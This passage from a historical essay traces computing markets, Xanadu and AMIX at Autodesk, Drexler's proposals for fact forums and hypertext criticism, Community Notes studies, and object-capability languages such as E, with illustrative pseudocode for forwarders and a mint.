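They also examined the kind of rising bids that Drexler and Miller had proposed, using a simple auction with three bidders whose bids grew by $1, $2 and $3 per round. The price averaged $6 but kept swinging between $3 and $8. Over a long period the bidders won time slices in the ratio 3.43:2:1, reasonably close to their funding ratio of 3:2:1, but over shorter periods their shares varied widely. Since the average price was the sum of the three rates, Waldspurger and colleagues realized that they didn't need the auction. A computer could divide its time directly in proportion to each program's funding, which would give fair shares and a steady price with much less communication.

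Other researchers continued to experiment with computing markets. In *A Market-Oriented Programming Environment and its Application to Distributed Multicommodity Flow Problems*, Wellman (1993) had software agents solve planning problems by computing the prices at which supply and demand in an artificial economy would balance. But few such systems went into regular use. Shneidman, Ng and colleagues observed in *Why Markets Could (But Don't Currently) Solve Resource Allocation Problems in Systems* that the approach had not caught on, although new projects appeared every few years. At about the same time, Kevin Lai of HP Labs asked why so many enthusiastic publications had led to so few working systems. He thought designers still doubted that the economic approach was useful or relevant to them, and he hoped to persuade them to build more such systems. Lai and Shneidman's group were sympathetic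 to computing markets, which makes their accounts of the poor record more convincing.

Cloud computing later brought such auctions to many more people. In 2009 Amazon began to sell its spare computing capacity at a "spot" price that moved with supply and demand. Customers stated the most they would pay, and Amazon shut down their machines when the price rose above that limit. In 2017 Amazon made prices change more gradually and stopped requiring bids, but the price remained useful without the auction, as it had with Spawn.

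Blockchains came closer to the original proposal. A blockchain is a shared record kept by many computers whose owners need not trust each other, and some blockchains also run programs. On Ethereum, which started in 2015, each step of a program uses a set amount of a unit called gas. Whoever starts the program pays for the gas and sets a limit on it. If the program reaches the limit, it stops and Ethereum undoes its changes, but the person who started it still owes the fee. The limit caps what a program can spend, as a small sum in an expense account does in Drexler and Miller's proposal.

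Ethereum's users at first paid whatever they bid for gas, so they had to guess what others were offering, a problem Drexler and Miller had warned of in such auctions. In 2021 its developers introduced a base fee that the system calculates from recent demand. Ethereum's charges for storage were further from the 1988 design. Users paid once to store data and owed no rent afterwards, so abandoned data stayed on every full copy of the current record. Miller later became chief scientist of Agoric, a blockchain company that lists the three papers as foundational.

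## 1979 to 1992: Xanadu and the American Information Exchange

While Miller and Drexler were planning markets for programs, some of their friends were building two services for people, which Miller helped design. Xanadu was to be a worldwide library that paid authors whenever anyone read or quoted their work. The American Information Exchange (AMIX) was an online market for reports, software and advice. Autodesk, which made drafting software, began funding both in 1988 and gave them up on 20 August 1992.

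### Quoting without copying

Ted Nelson started work on the ideas behind Xanadu in 1960, as a graduate student at Harvard. He later coined the word "hypertext" for writing whose links let readers take many paths through it. Nelson (2000) described the goal as a literature in which links keep working when documents change, readers can see where every quotation came from, and anyone can quote as much as they like without negotiating.

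All of this depended on giving every piece of text a permanent address, which Xanadu's programmers called a tumbler. A tumbler is a row of numbers, with zeros separating the fields. In the invented address 1.42.0.7.0.15.2.0.1.300, the text is on server 1.42, belongs to account 7, and is in the second version of document 15. In the last field, 1 means text (2 would mean links) and 300 means the 300th character. Any field can grow, so the owner of document 15 can number a new version without asking a central office. Readers can link to any stretch of text, even if its author hasn't marked it.

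Suppose Alice publishes an article, and Bob quotes 200 characters of it in a 1,000-character essay. His essay stores the addresses of those characters instead of a copy, and Xanadu fetches the characters whenever someone opens the essay. Nelson called this transclusion. If Alice adds a paragraph at the top of her article, Bob's quotation stays intact, because the old characters keep their permanent addresses and only the list that puts them in order changes.

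The programmers made this fast by using tree structures called enfilades, which they kept secret for decades. Project Xanadu (1999) finally named three of them in a short history. The granfilade stored the text, the poomfilade recorded the order in which each document used it, and the spanfilade found every document that used a given passage. A reader of Alice's article could therefore find Bob's essay and follow links from either end. Links on the Web work in only one direction, so Alice may never learn that Bob has linked to her.

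Transclusion also gave Xanadu a way to calculate royalties. If a reader paid 10 cents for Bob's essay and every character cost the same, Alice would receive 2 cents and Bob 8. The rules forbade ordinary copying, but no software could have stopped a reader from retyping Alice's words.

Anyone could write down a tumbler and pass it on, but it gave no right to read a private document, so it was not a capability. The 17 design principles that the essayist Gwern Branwen reproduces in *Project Xanadu* (2025) instead call for secure identification of every user and access controls on documents.

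### Two unfinished versions

Nelson, who was not a programmer, brought together a small group in Swarthmore, Pennsylvania, in the summer of 1979. It included Miller, then a student at Yale, and Roger Gregory, who had repaired used computers for a living. They planned to write the program in three months but spent most of the time on its design, according to Wolf's *Wired* article *The Curse of Xanadu* (1995). Gregory kept the project going for years afterwards with his consulting income and a changing group of volunteers. Drexler often visited and offered friendly criticism. Another volunteer, Chip Morningstar, recalled in the Computer History Museum's *Oral History of Chip Morningstar* (2019) that when people at trade shows asked what the job paid, the usual reply was to ask how much money they had.

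In October 1987 Gregory met John Walker, a founder of Autodesk, at a programmers' conference. Autodesk had begun as a partnership with little capital and a drafting program of about 12,000 lines, according to *Autodesk Company History* (2025), an article in *IEEE Annals of the History of Computing*. By 1987 its sales had passed $79 million a year, so it could afford a risky investment, and it bought 80 percent of Gregory's company. In *Xanadu*, a statement for the press conference on 8 April, Walker (1988) promised a first product within 18 months. Under a contract called the Silver Agreement, Nelson kept the right to run a publishing network with royalties but gave up control of the software's development. Wolf dates this contract to 1988, but Project Xanadu dates it to 1983.

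Gregory already had a partly working server, the program that would store the library and send text to readers. The test version he sent to some users didn't work. Miller concluded that repairs would not be enough. The program handled transclusion clumsily, could not keep track of versions, had no security features and ran slowly. Miller and the project's manager, Marc Stiegler, decided to start again.

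The programmers wrote the new version in Smalltalk, a language that makes it easy to try out designs, and planned to translate it into C++ for the finished product. Michael McClary, who worked on the translation, often found the design had changed before he could begin. A former Xanadu programmer told Branwen that converting and compiling the program took about a week. By December 1990 the product was more than a year late, and Autodesk's head of marketing was joking about the day it would ship (Los Angeles Times, 1990).

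Neither version became a product. In 1999 the company published the code of both, naming Gregory's version Udanax Green and its replacement Udanax Gold.

### One sale on AMIX

AMIX was the idea of Phil Salin, an economist who also helped negotiate Xanadu's deal with Autodesk. Online services of the 1980s, such as CompuServe, sold information to their subscribers, but Salin wanted subscribers to sell it to each other. Autodesk took a majority stake in AMIX in June 1988, as Tech Monitor's *Autodesk Buys American Information Exchange Stake* (1988) reported. Morningstar led the engineers who built the service.

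In *AMIX Introduction*, Whitaker (1992) forwarded the company's own description of AMIX to several mailing lists and a few individuals, including Tim Berners-Lee, the inventor of the Web. Customers dialled in from a PC and browsed listings by subject. Sellers could offer documents, such as a market report or a piece of source code, for $1 to $500. Consultants could also list themselves and take on contracts worth up to $2,000. AMIX charged the seller 40 percent of the first $50 of each payment, 25 percent of the next $50, 15 percent of the next $400 and 10 percent of anything above $500.

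Morningstar (2020), in *What Agoric Learned from the American Information Exchange About Online Markets*, explains AMIX contracts with the example of a $500 article, with half the price due on agreement and half on delivery. At the 1992 rates, the sale would have gone like this:

1. The buyer posts a request, and a writer responds. A structured form of email leads them through the negotiation.
2. When they agree, AMIX takes $250 from the buyer's account. It keeps $20 of the first $50, $12.50 of the next $50 and $22.50 of the remaining $150, which comes to $55. The writer gets $195.
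3. The writer delivers the article through AMIX. The system checks the date, takes the other $250 and pays the writer another $195.

The buyer has paid $500, the writer has earned $390 and AMIX has kept $110. AMIX treated each instalment as a separate sale, so a single payment on delivery would have reduced the fee to $92.50. AMIX took the largest share of the price on cheap items, leaving the seller of a $10 report with only $6, although it advertised itself as a place to sell small, inexpensive reports.

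Information is awkward to sell, because a buyer who has read a report to see if it is worth the price no longer needs to buy it. AMIX therefore showed buyers comments from earlier customers and a record of how often a seller's deals had ended in dispute. The system could check whether an article had arrived on time, but not whether it was any good. Buyer and seller could agree in advance on a number of revisions, a partial payment for unsatisfactory work, or a neutral arbitrator. If a dispute went to arbitration, the system could send the arbitrator the work and a full record of the negotiation.

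These arrangements dealt with fraud, which the agoric papers had mostly left customers to guard against. AMIX made cheats easier to recognise and gave their victims a way to get money back. But everyone had to trust the company that kept the accounts, and buyers' comments could not warn of flaws they had missed.

Autodesk's managers had trouble seeing the point of AMIX. In a memo to them, *Understanding AMIX*, Walker (1989) compared it to Federal Express, which had created a market for overnight delivery when hardly anyone had known the demand existed. He thought the delays in writing the software were no worse than those of Autodesk's own products. He also warned that finishing the software would only give AMIX a chance to succeed.

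### Autodesk withdraws

AMIX opened a pilot service on 2 January 1992 and planned its official launch for the autumn. In February, Autodesk announced poor sales. Its shares, which had sold for more than $60 in 1991, fell to about $23. Carol Bartz became chief executive that spring and reviewed the company's projects. Autodesk's *Farewell, Xanadu* (1992), which collects the announcements of 20 August, says she dropped Xanadu and AMIX because neither fitted the company's main business of design software. Autodesk gave its stakes in the two companies back to them and ended its support after 30 days.

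AMIX thus lost its funding just before its launch. In a later note on his website, Fourmilab, Walker called it "an idea yet untested". He was more confident in Fourmilab's *CONTINUITY* (2021), where he suggested that with Autodesk's support AMIX might have filled the place that eBay later took. Like AMIX, eBay let strangers trade and rate each other. But eBay sold physical goods to anyone with a Web browser, while AMIX sold information to people who had paid $50 to join, installed its software and dialled in at $3 an hour or more. The pilot was too short to show whether enough people would have joined on those terms.

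### Why Xanadu never shipped

Gregory blamed the decision to start again. He told Wolf that his version had been within six months of shipping when Miller and Stiegler abandoned it. Miller told Wolf that the new version was also about six months from completion when Autodesk withdrew. Neither estimate is convincing. Gregory's test version had failed, and Rob Jellinghaus, who worked on the new version after Autodesk left, found that it was slow and took about 20 lines of difficult C++ just to retrieve a piece of text.

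Walker blamed excessive ambition. He wrote that the team had entered a "techno-hubris zone", where it tried to design a complete system for all the world's information before releasing anything. He had encouraged this himself in his 1988 statement, where he praised Xanadu for rejecting every limit on its size and generality and said that nothing less ambitious could be as useful. But he had also planned to release a small first version and let customers guide later development. The programmers never got that guidance. When Jonathan Shapiro, whom they had hired to write documentation, asked them to describe a typical customer, they gave vague answers.

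Branwen doubts that transclusion would have had many uses even if Xanadu had been finished, because few texts need detailed commentary alongside them. At a party in 2024, Branwen saw a Xanadu demonstration in which lines ran across the screen from the Book of Genesis to commentaries on it, and found it unreadable. That is a good argument against Nelson's screen layout but a weaker one against transclusion, which Branwen's own website uses heavily in pop-up windows that show material from other pages.

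The Web helps to explain why later attempts to revive Xanadu failed, though it came too late to explain why the project missed its 1989 deadline. Berners-Lee had left out two-way links, version tracking and royalties, and anyone could build tools for what remained. Miller told Wolf, as a criticism, that what the Web did was easy, but that ease was also a reason the Web spread so quickly.

Wolf interviewed most of the main participants, and his article is still the most detailed account of the project. It also dwells on Nelson's attention disorder and Gregory's depression. Nelson called the article "libelous" in a 1996 interview that Grand Text Auto (2004) quotes. He objected that Wolf portrayed the team as blundering hobbyists and was much nastier about Gregory than about him. Wolf's evidence partly supports Nelson. From 1988 to 1992 Nelson had no direct role in managing the software, so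 his trouble finishing things explains little about those years. The programmers who led the redesign had come from Xerox PARC, one of the best computing laboratories in the world.

Stevens (2023), in *Code and Critique*, argues that historians have put too much weight on Xanadu as software. He studied Nelson's writings from 1960 to 1981 and concluded that Xanadu was more important as a model of how media could give people greater freedom to think and communicate. This reading helps explain Nelson's long opposition to the Web, which he considers a poor version of hypertext. It is less helpful for judging the Autodesk years, when the company paid programmers to deliver a product.

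### What the programmers did next

Neither project had tested the main proposal of the agoric papers. The traders on AMIX were people, and the programs that served them all belonged to one company. But both projects produced ideas that outlasted them. Around 1989 Miller, Jellinghaus and their colleague Dean Tribble worked out how a program could send requests to the result of an earlier request before that result had arrived, which greatly reduces waiting on a slow network. In about 1990 Robin Hanson, then an AI researcher and later an economist, ran one of the first prediction markets inside a company, in which Xanadu's staff bet on questions such as whether cold fusion was real.

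Morningstar says that AMIX influenced Nick Szabo, who introduced the term "smart contract" for agreements that software helps to carry out. According to a 2026 review from the University of Minnesota, Kelsie Nabben's book *Decentralised Digital Security* treats the Xanadu and AMIX communities and the cypherpunks, who promoted cryptography to protect privacy, as forerunners of today's work on network security.

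Several of the programmers went on to work on capabilities. Shapiro, who briefly ran Xanadu's company after Autodesk left, built the EROS operating system. Miller and Tribble turned to programming languages. Morningstar founded Electric Communities with Douglas Crockford and Randy Farmer, who had worked with him on AMIX. They wanted to build a virtual world in which users could add their own objects and run parts of the world on their own computers. Stiegler joined them and kept a colour-coded chart of the work. He added purple for tasks that would require a PhD thesis, and there were many of them. The company went bankrupt in 2001, but its programmers had by then created the E language, because such a world needed a safe way to run programs written by strangers.

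## Since 1986: hypertext publishing and debate about dangerous technologies

Drexler wanted Xanadu to help people debate dangerous technologies, a more urgent use than paying authors. In *Engines of Creation* (1986), a book for general readers, he predicted machines that would build things atom by atom, including copies of themselves, and AI that would greatly speed up engineering. He thought competition made it almost impossible to stop either technology, but that people could get better at finding mistakes in their plans before acting on them. He proposed public hearings on technical facts, and a hypertext library where readers could see the objections to whatever they were reading. Customers in an agoric market could also have used such a library to learn about cheats.

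### Hearings on technical facts

Drexler complained that governments and companies settled technical questions in secret expert committees, while their opponents argued about them in the press. He expected harder questions to come, such as whether a self-copying machine was safe or whether we can "trust this AI system."

Drexler took his remedy from the physicist Arthur Kantrowitz, who had advised NASA to reach the Moon with several smaller rockets joined in orbit instead of one giant one. By Drexler's account, nobody answered Kantrowitz's arguments, and the report that supported him ended up in a White House safe. The giant rockets did reach the Moon, so the story is better evidence of a closed debate than of a wrong decision. Kantrowitz concluded that technical disputes needed some of the procedures of a court. Journalists called his idea a science court, but Drexler preferred "fact forum"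 and kept "science court" for forums run by governments.

In a fact forum, each side lists what it considers the key facts, in order of importance. A referee starts at the top of each list and leads rounds of argument, cross-examination and negotiation to find statements both sides will accept. A technical panel then writes an opinion on whatever is still in dispute, setting out what is known and what is uncertain. The panellists come from related fields, because specialists involved in the dispute would be biased. Each side can reject candidates for the panel. The forum makes no policy recommendations.

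Kantrowitz tried this at the University of California, Berkeley, with the geneticist Beverly Paigen and the biochemist William Havender, who had argued in public about birth defects and genetic damage at Love Canal, a chemical dump in New York State. The two met over several weeks, then cross-examined each other before a panel of graduate students. They and the panel agreed on eleven statements of fact and clarified what they still disagreed about. By June 1985, Kantrowitz had run two more forums, at Dartmouth College, on ballistic missile defence. Ford, Carter and Reagan all endorsed the science court as presidential candidates, but none of them set one up as president.

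The Berkeley trial suggests that opponents may agree on more than they appear to in public, but both participants had chosen to take part. Drexler expected that anyone who refused would lose credibility. That would happen only if the public noticed, and a company with a hazardous product might prefer a little suspicion to a cross-examination. Facts are also hard to separate from values. Drexler would have counted a statement as factual if an experiment or observation could in principle disprove it. "This dump is dangerous" might pass that test, but how much evidence people demand before accepting it depends partly on whether they are more afraid of wrongly accepting it or wrongly rejecting it.

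### A false claim on paper and in hypertext

A forum takes weeks to deal with one dispute, so Drexler expected forums to cover only a fraction of the facts that mattered. He wanted hypertext for the rest, and took Xanadu as his model. His 1987 paper, *Hypertext Publishing and the Evolution of Knowledge*, set out the requirements. As Tom Breeden summarises them in a review, readers should be able to follow links in both directions and comment on a single sentence. The system should be open to the public, pay royalties, and filter links according to each reader's preferences.

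Drexler thought that knowledge evolves as people produce ideas, spread them and test them. Paper worked well enough for producing and spreading ideas, but poorly for testing them. For example, a journal article might state that a new self-copying machine can't survive outside its tank because it needs a chemical that doesn't occur in nature. A chemist who reads the article might know that the chemical occurs in pine resin.

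In paper publishing, she writes to the journal, which prints her letter eight months later. By then the article is in hundreds of libraries, and those copies don't refer to her letter. An engineer who finds the article three years later could look for replies in a citation index, but in 1986 only research libraries had citation indexes, which covered limited topics and were months out of date. He probably doesn't look, and he repeats the claim in a safety report. Its readers are even less likely to find the letter.

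In Drexler's system, the chemist publishes two sentences about pine resin and links them to the incorrect sentence. She can do this without permission to alter the article, and its author can't remove her link. The engineer sees a mark beside the claim and opens her reply. If the author accepts the correction, he publishes a new version and labels the old one "retracted", but the old one stays available. Because links work in both directions, anyone can also find the safety reports that cite the article and attach the same correction to them.

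Open publishing would also fill the system with rubbish, so readers would need filters. A cautious reader could choose to see only documents from established publishers. Others could see whatever people they respected had recommended. Royalties would encourage editors to compile competing guides to the best material.

Drexler thought the most important benefit of hypertext publishing would be that readers could notice when objections were missing. In print, a lack of known criticism means little, because short criticisms are hard to publish and hard to find. If critics could attach objections easily, an important claim that had none would deserve more trust, but only if competent people had examined it.

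### CritLink and other annotation tools

Several programmers tried to add two-way links to the Web, and had to decide who would control them. Hanson's *Projects to add "backlinks" to the web* lists a 1995 plan by John Walker of Autodesk to show incoming links only where a document's author allowed them. This design was easy to build, but it let the people with the most to fear from criticism hide it.

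Ka-Ping Yee, a student at the University of Waterloo who worked with the Foresight Institute, found a way for readers to comment on a web page without its author's consent. He released CritLink in July 1997. Yee (1997) wrote in *CRIT Mediator* that he presented it that summer at a conference of extropians, who were enthusiasts for future technology. CritLink used a mediator, a server between the reader and the Web. When a reader put crit.org in front of a page's address, the mediator fetched the page, looked in its database for comments, and sent the reader a copy with the comments marked. The original page didn't change, and the reader needed no special software. Each comment was itself a web page, so people could comment on comments, as Yee (1999) pointed out in a message to a Web standards mailing list.

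Jones described how CritLink worked in practice in *Foresight web enhancement*, a talk she gave for the institute at Stanford in 2000. Small coloured triangles marked each comment as support, an issue, a question or a remark. Nobody could delete a comment, but if an author corrected the words it referred to, it moved to the bottom of the page. The institute's members used CritLink to revise a policy document on nanotechnology until they all accepted it, and to mark up a *Scientific American* article from April 1996 that many of them considered unfair.

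In the second case, when half a dozen people commented on one paragraph, the triangles ran across the screen and readers struggled to find anything. Jones concluded that CritLink worked best for single documents. The site was down on the day of Jones's talk. According to the Foresight Institute's programme for a 1998 meeting, Drexler had presented CritLink to the institute's supporters as "The Other Half of Hypertext" and had linked it to their chances of surviving the technological turmoil ahead.

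Other groups built similar tools. *Annotea* (Kahan, Koivunen and colleagues, 2001) describes one developed by the Web's standards body, which kept comments on separate servers. Harvard's law school used its *Annotation Engine* for public comment on draft legal documents, and noted that Third Voice, a commercial rival, had already closed. Google opened a comment service called Sidewiki in 2009 and shut it two years later. Hypothesis, a nonprofit founded in 2011, has lasted, mostly because teachers use it for class discussions. All of these tools showed comments only to people who had chosen to use them, so the comments rarely reached the readers a false claim was misleading.

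In *Engines of Creation 2.0*, Drexler (2006) complained that readers of a controversial document on the Web still couldn't easily see its best-rated criticisms. He thought his own work had suffered from this. In 1986 he had imagined tiny self-copying machines as the basis of manufacturing. By 1992 he had worked out that factories would be simpler and more efficient without them, but novels and films had already spread the idea of swarms of these machines eating the world. He blamed the resulting fears for the US government's refusal to consider his proposals. That explanation is convenient for him because it blames a misunderstanding. The episode is also a problem for his theory, because people who met the swarms in a film would not have seen a correction attached to his book.

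### Community Notes

The largest test of attached criticism began in 2021, when Twitter (now X) started the programme it later named Community Notes. Volunteers write short notes on misleading posts, and other volunteers rate the notes. X shows the successful notes under the post to everyone who sees it, and the post's author can't remove them.

Counting votes would let the larger political camp decide which notes appear. *Birdwatch* (Wojcik, Hilgard and colleagues, 2022) explains how X's engineers avoided this. A program looks for the values that best predict each person's rating of each note, using the formula:

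predicted rating = m + g + h + (v × s)

Here m is the average of all ratings, g is how generous this rater usually is, and s is the note's slant towards one viewpoint. The program infers the rater's viewpoint, v, from past ratings. The remainder, h, is the note's appeal to people of any viewpoint, and X normally shows a note only if h is at least 0.4.

Suppose m is 0.5, and two raters of ordinary generosity (g = 0) have opposite viewpoints, +1 and −1. If both give a note the top rating of 1, its h is 0.5 and its slant is zero, so it can appear. If the first rater gives the note 1 and the second gives it 0, its h is zero and its slant is 0.5, so it stays hidden. The real system needs more raters and makes further checks.

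Public notes substantially reduce engagement with a post once they appear. In *Community Notes Reduce Engagement with and Diffusion of False Information Online* (2025), Slaughter, Peytavin and colleagues tracked about 40,000 posts for which volunteers had proposed notes. They compared each post that received a public note with a combination of posts that had been spreading similarly but had no public note. After the note was attached, a post received about 46 percent fewer reposts and about 44 percent fewer likes than the comparison predicted. Over the post's whole life, reposts fell by only about 12 percent, because most sharing happened before the note appeared.

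This delay helps explain why *Did the Roll-Out of Community Notes Reduce Engagement With Misinformation on X/Twitter?* (Chuai, Tian and colleagues, 2024) found no significant reduction in reposts and likes of misleading posts as X made notes visible to more users. Notes can work well on the posts that get them and still make little difference overall if they are late and rare.

Drexler had also hoped that authors would withdraw their errors. Gao, Zhang and Rui tested something close to this in *Can Crowdchecking Curb Misinformation?* (2025). They compared posts whose notes had just reached the threshold for public display with posts whose notes had just missed it, since the two groups should otherwise be much alike. Authors were about 32 percent more likely to delete a post if the note was public. Drexler wanted the old version to remain, with a label, but deletion removes both the claim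 and its refutation.

Reposts and deletions don't measure whether readers judge claims better, which was Drexler's main concern. *Community Notes Increase Trust in Fact-Checking on Social Media* (Drolsbach, Solovev and Pröllochs, 2024) comes closer to measuring this. In a survey experiment with 1,810 Americans, people on both the political left and right trusted notes that explained the error more than they trusted plain warning labels. This supports Drexler's idea of linking a claim to the reasons against it. But fact-checking social media posts is very different from settling a dispute over the safety of a new technology, where readers may be unable to follow the reasons.

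### Who writes criticism, and who sees it

Critics can't keep up with everything people publish. A false claim may take a minute to invent and a day to refute. The hypertext researcher Mark Bernstein, in *Links* (2018), regretted that he and his colleagues had built systems that "asymmetrically advantage liars". AI may reduce this advantage, since it can draft refutations as easily as false claims. In 2025 X began to let AI programs propose notes on posts, but human volunteers still rate the notes, so the volunteers' time limits how many can be reviewed.

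Royalties could make matters worse, because an exciting falsehood would probably earn more than a dull correction. X also pays some authors for the attention their posts attract, and in 2023 it stopped paying for posts that a note had corrected. A hypertext publisher could do the same, but somebody would have to decide which corrections were right.

If readers choose their own filters, many will choose critics who already share their opinions. Drexler wanted readers to notice when a claim had no objections, but their filters may be hiding the objections. X avoids this by using one filter for everyone, but that filter hides notes on subjects that divide people. For its report *Rated Not Helpful*, the Center for Countering Digital Hate, a campaign group often in conflict with X, studied 283 misleading posts about the 2024 US election. Volunteers had proposed accurate notes for all of them,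 but X did not show these notes to all users on 209 of the posts. The group chose the posts itself, so this share may not be typical.

X's test also measures agreement between people who usually disagree, not their understanding of the subject. That may be enough to judge a doctored photograph, but for a claim about a self-copying machine or an AI system, Drexler's fact forum has an advantage because its panel must be technically competent.

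Neither method helps much with claims that nobody publishes. If a laboratory keeps its test results private, outside critics have no text to attach an objection to, and a forum can't cross-examine a company that declines to take part. Drexler also warned in 1986 that a worldwide hypertext library might not have time to mature before the breakthroughs in nanotechnology and AI arrived.

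## 1992 to 2006: Joule, E and the theory of object capabilities

Criticism can warn people only about flaws that somebody has found, so people who run strangers' programs also need protection from undiscovered flaws. In the 1990s, several former Xanadu programmers tried to provide this protection through programming languages in which code starts with no access to anything and can use only the capabilities that other code gives it.

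### From Joule to E

Dean Tribble, Miller and Norm Hardy helped design Joule, a language for programs spread over many machines. The announcement of a 2006 talk by Miller lists Joule as work for Fujitsu and Agorics, a software company that came before the blockchain company Agoric. Joule objects sent each other messages without waiting for replies, so many parts of a program could run at once. Each program ran in one or more "tanks", each of which could fail, move to another machine or run short of memory without affecting the others.

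Electric Communities needed something similar for its virtual world. Its programmers took Java, removed the features that let code get around capabilities, and added Joule's style of messages. They used the result, now known as Original-E, to build EC Habitats, a graphical world. When the company's plans changed, its board released the language as open source. Miller and a group of volunteers turned it into E, with support from Hewlett-Packard and Combex, a small company. Miller set out the language and the theory behind it in his doctoral thesis, *Robust Composition* (2006), which Jonathan Shapiro advised.

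E gave objects the property rights that Miller and Drexler had described in their 1988 agoric proposal, but it did not make objects pay for processor time or memory. Joule had at least borrowed KeyKOS's methods for rationing these resources, but E had not yet done so by 2006. A hostile object in E could not open a file without a capability to it, but it could delay neighbouring objects by running in an endless loop.

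### How to make a capability language

Languages such as Java are close to capability languages, because their objects affect each other mainly through references. To turn one into a capability language, a designer has to block the other ways its objects can affect each other.

One of these is direct access to memory. A C++ program can turn any number into a memory address, so it can guess where an object is and read or change its contents. A memory-safe language such as Java does not allow this.

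Another is global access to files and the network. Here is a word counter in an ordinary language:

```
function countWords(name):
    file = openFile(name)
    return number of words in file.read()
```

Every part of the program can call `openFile`, including a library that somebody added only to format dates. In a capability language, the caller has to supply the file:

```
function countWords(file):
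    return number of words in file.read()
```

This function can't open anything else, because `openFile` has no meaning inside it unless someone passes it in. Java fails this test because it has built-in classes that open files and connections, and code can use some of them just by writing their names. Whoever loads the code can't withhold those classes. E also gives a few names, such as `true`, the same meaning in all code, but Miller points out that these names provide no authority.

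Shared variables are a less obvious route. A Java class can have a "static" variable that many objects can read and change, so two objects that nobody has introduced to each other could use it to exchange data or even capabilities. Joe-E, a restricted version of Java, allows static variables only if their contents can never change.

Once the designer has closed these routes, an object can affect the world only by sending messages to objects it has references to. Apart from the references it had when the system started, it can gain references only in the three ways that Miller and Drexler listed. To work out the worst that unfamiliar code could do, a programmer can therefore start from the references it receives, without reading the code itself.

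### A forwarder that Alice can switch off

Redell's forwarder, which lets Alice take back access she has given to Bob, takes only a few lines in a language like this. In simplified pseudocode:

```
function makeForwarder(target):
    enabled = true

    function forward(request):
        if not enabled: fail
        return target.handle(request)

    function switchOff():
        enabled = false

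    return forward, switchOff
```

Alice calls `makeForwarder(report)`, gives `forward` to Bob and keeps `switchOff`. Both functions share the variable `enabled`, which code outside `makeForwarder` cannot access. Bob's requests go through until Alice calls `switchOff`, and then they fail. She could also add a line that rejects every request except "read", or one that counts requests and rejects any after the hundredth.

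This version has a weakness if the target hands out further capabilities. Suppose Alice shares a folder, and Bob requests a file in it through the forwarder. The folder returns a direct capability to the file, which still works after Alice switches off the forwarder. Miller's solution, called a membrane, puts a new forwarder around every capability that passes through in either direction, and one switch disables them all. It lets plain data through unwrapped, since nobody can take back what Bob has already read.

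### A mint and its purses

In *Capability-based Financial Instruments*, Miller, Morningstar and Frantz (2000) proposed building electronic contracts from small reusable objects. Without these, each new arrangement between people who distrusted one another seemed to need its own cryptographic protocol, which was difficult and expensive to design. Their best-known example is a mint, which creates a currency and the purses that hold it.

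The mint uses a sealer and a matching unsealer. The sealer puts an object in a box that only that unsealer can open, so anyone can hold the box but only the mint's code can use the object inside.

```
function makeMint():
    seal, unseal = a new matching pair

    function makePurse(balance):
        function take(amount):
            if amount < 0 or amount > balance: fail
            balance = balance - amount

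        purse = new object with these functions:
            getBalance():   return balance
            newPurse():     return makePurse(0)
            getSealed():    return seal(take)
            deposit(amount, source):
                takeFrom = unseal(source.getSealed())
                takeFrom(amount)
                balance = balance + amount
        return purse

    return makePurse
```

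Whoever calls `makeMint` receives `makePurse` and can create money with it, for example by calling `makePurse(100)`. Everyone else has only purses, and a purse can make only empty purses.

Suppose Alice has a purse holding 100 and wants to pay Bob 10. If she sent him that purse, he could empty it, so she uses it to create a new, empty purse and deposits 10 from the old purse into the new one. To make the deposit, the new purse gets the old one's `take` function in a sealed box, opens the box and calls `take(10)`. The old balance falls to 90, and the new purse adds 10 to its own. Alice sends the new purse to Bob with her order. She might have kept a reference to it, so Bob immediately deposits the 10 in a purse that only he holds.

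| Step | Alice's purse | Payment purse | Bob's purse |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice asks for an empty purse | 100 | 0 | 0 |
| The payment purse deposits 10 from Alice's | 90 | 10 | 0 |
| Bob's purse deposits 10 from the payment purse | 90 | 0 | 10 |

The total is 100 after each step. If Bob tries to deposit 11, `take` fails before his balance changes. A negative deposit fails at the same check. If Alice sends a fake purse that reports a balance of a million, it can't produce a box that the mint's unsealer will open unless it gets one from a real purse. The money then comes out of the real purse.

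The mint is a working version of the expense accounts in the agoric papers. A hijacked AI agent with a purse of 10 could still waste the 10, since the code cannot evaluate what the money buys. Everyone who accepts the currency must also trust whoever holds `makePurse` and the machine that runs the mint.

### Vats, messages and promises

E groups objects into containers called vats, which developed from Joule's tanks. Each vat runs on one machine at a time and finishes handling one message before it starts the next. An object can call another object in the same vat and wait for the answer, as in most languages. It can also send a message without waiting, which is the only way to reach an object in a different vat. The message then joins the receiving vat's queue.

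Miller's example is an account that reports each change in its balance to a list of other objects, including a spreadsheet. If the account calls the spreadsheet and waits, the spreadsheet's code runs while the account is partway through its list. That code could crash, and the rest of the list would never receive the report. It could also trigger another payment, and some objects would then receive the newer balance before the older one. If the account sends its reports without waiting, it finishes its own work first, and the spreadsheet can't interrupt it. The mint needs the same protection because, halfway through a deposit, the money has left one purse and not yet reached the other. No other message can interrupt the deposit at that point.

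An object that doesn't wait needs a way to refer to an answer it hasn't received. E immediately gives it a promise, which stands for the future result and can receive messages. Suppose the mint is in Tokyo, Alice is in New York, and a round trip takes 0.2 seconds. Alice asks for an empty purse, tells it to deposit 10, and asks for its balance. If she waited for each answer, the three requests would take 0.6 seconds. With promises, she sends all three at once, addressing the second and third to the purse that the first will create, and gets the balance after 0.2 seconds. The method came from Xanadu, and Barbara Liskov and Liuba Shrira had already published it in 1988.

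Alice can even send Bob a reference to the payment purse before the purse exists. E guarantees that Bob's messages to the purse will arrive after those Alice had already sent, so his request can't reach it before her deposit.

Vats never wait for one another, so they avoid deadlock, in which two programs stop forever because each is waiting for something the other holds. Programmers using E could still create a promise that depended on its own result. Miller knew of only two such errors in two large systems and the work of about 60 programmers, though he accepted that others might have gone unnoticed.

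When a network connection fails, every reference that crosses it breaks and stays broken, even after the network recovers. An object can register to be notified of the break and then use a stored address to get a new reference. It can't always determine whether its last messages arrived, so Alice may have to check her balance to learn whether she has paid.

E encrypts messages between machines and makes references across the network practically impossible to guess. But it has to send these references as data, so a hostile machine can pass them to anyone it can communicate with. E can therefore fully enforce its rules about who can introduce whom only on machines that run it faithfully.

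### What an access diagram leaves out

Security researchers often draw a system as a diagram, with an arrow from each program to everything it has permission to use. In *Paradigm Regained*, Miller and Shapiro argued that these diagrams had misled researchers for decades because they omit what the programs do with their permissions. Miller's thesis developed the argument into a set of bounds on what a program could eventually cause.

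Alice's forwarder shows the difference. Bob has an arrow to the forwarder, and the forwarder has an arrow to the report.

| What the analyst considers | Assumption | Bob's access to the report |
|---|---|---|
| Current permissions | Only direct arrows matter | None |
| The whole diagram | Any program may pass on anything it can | Possibly full and permanent |
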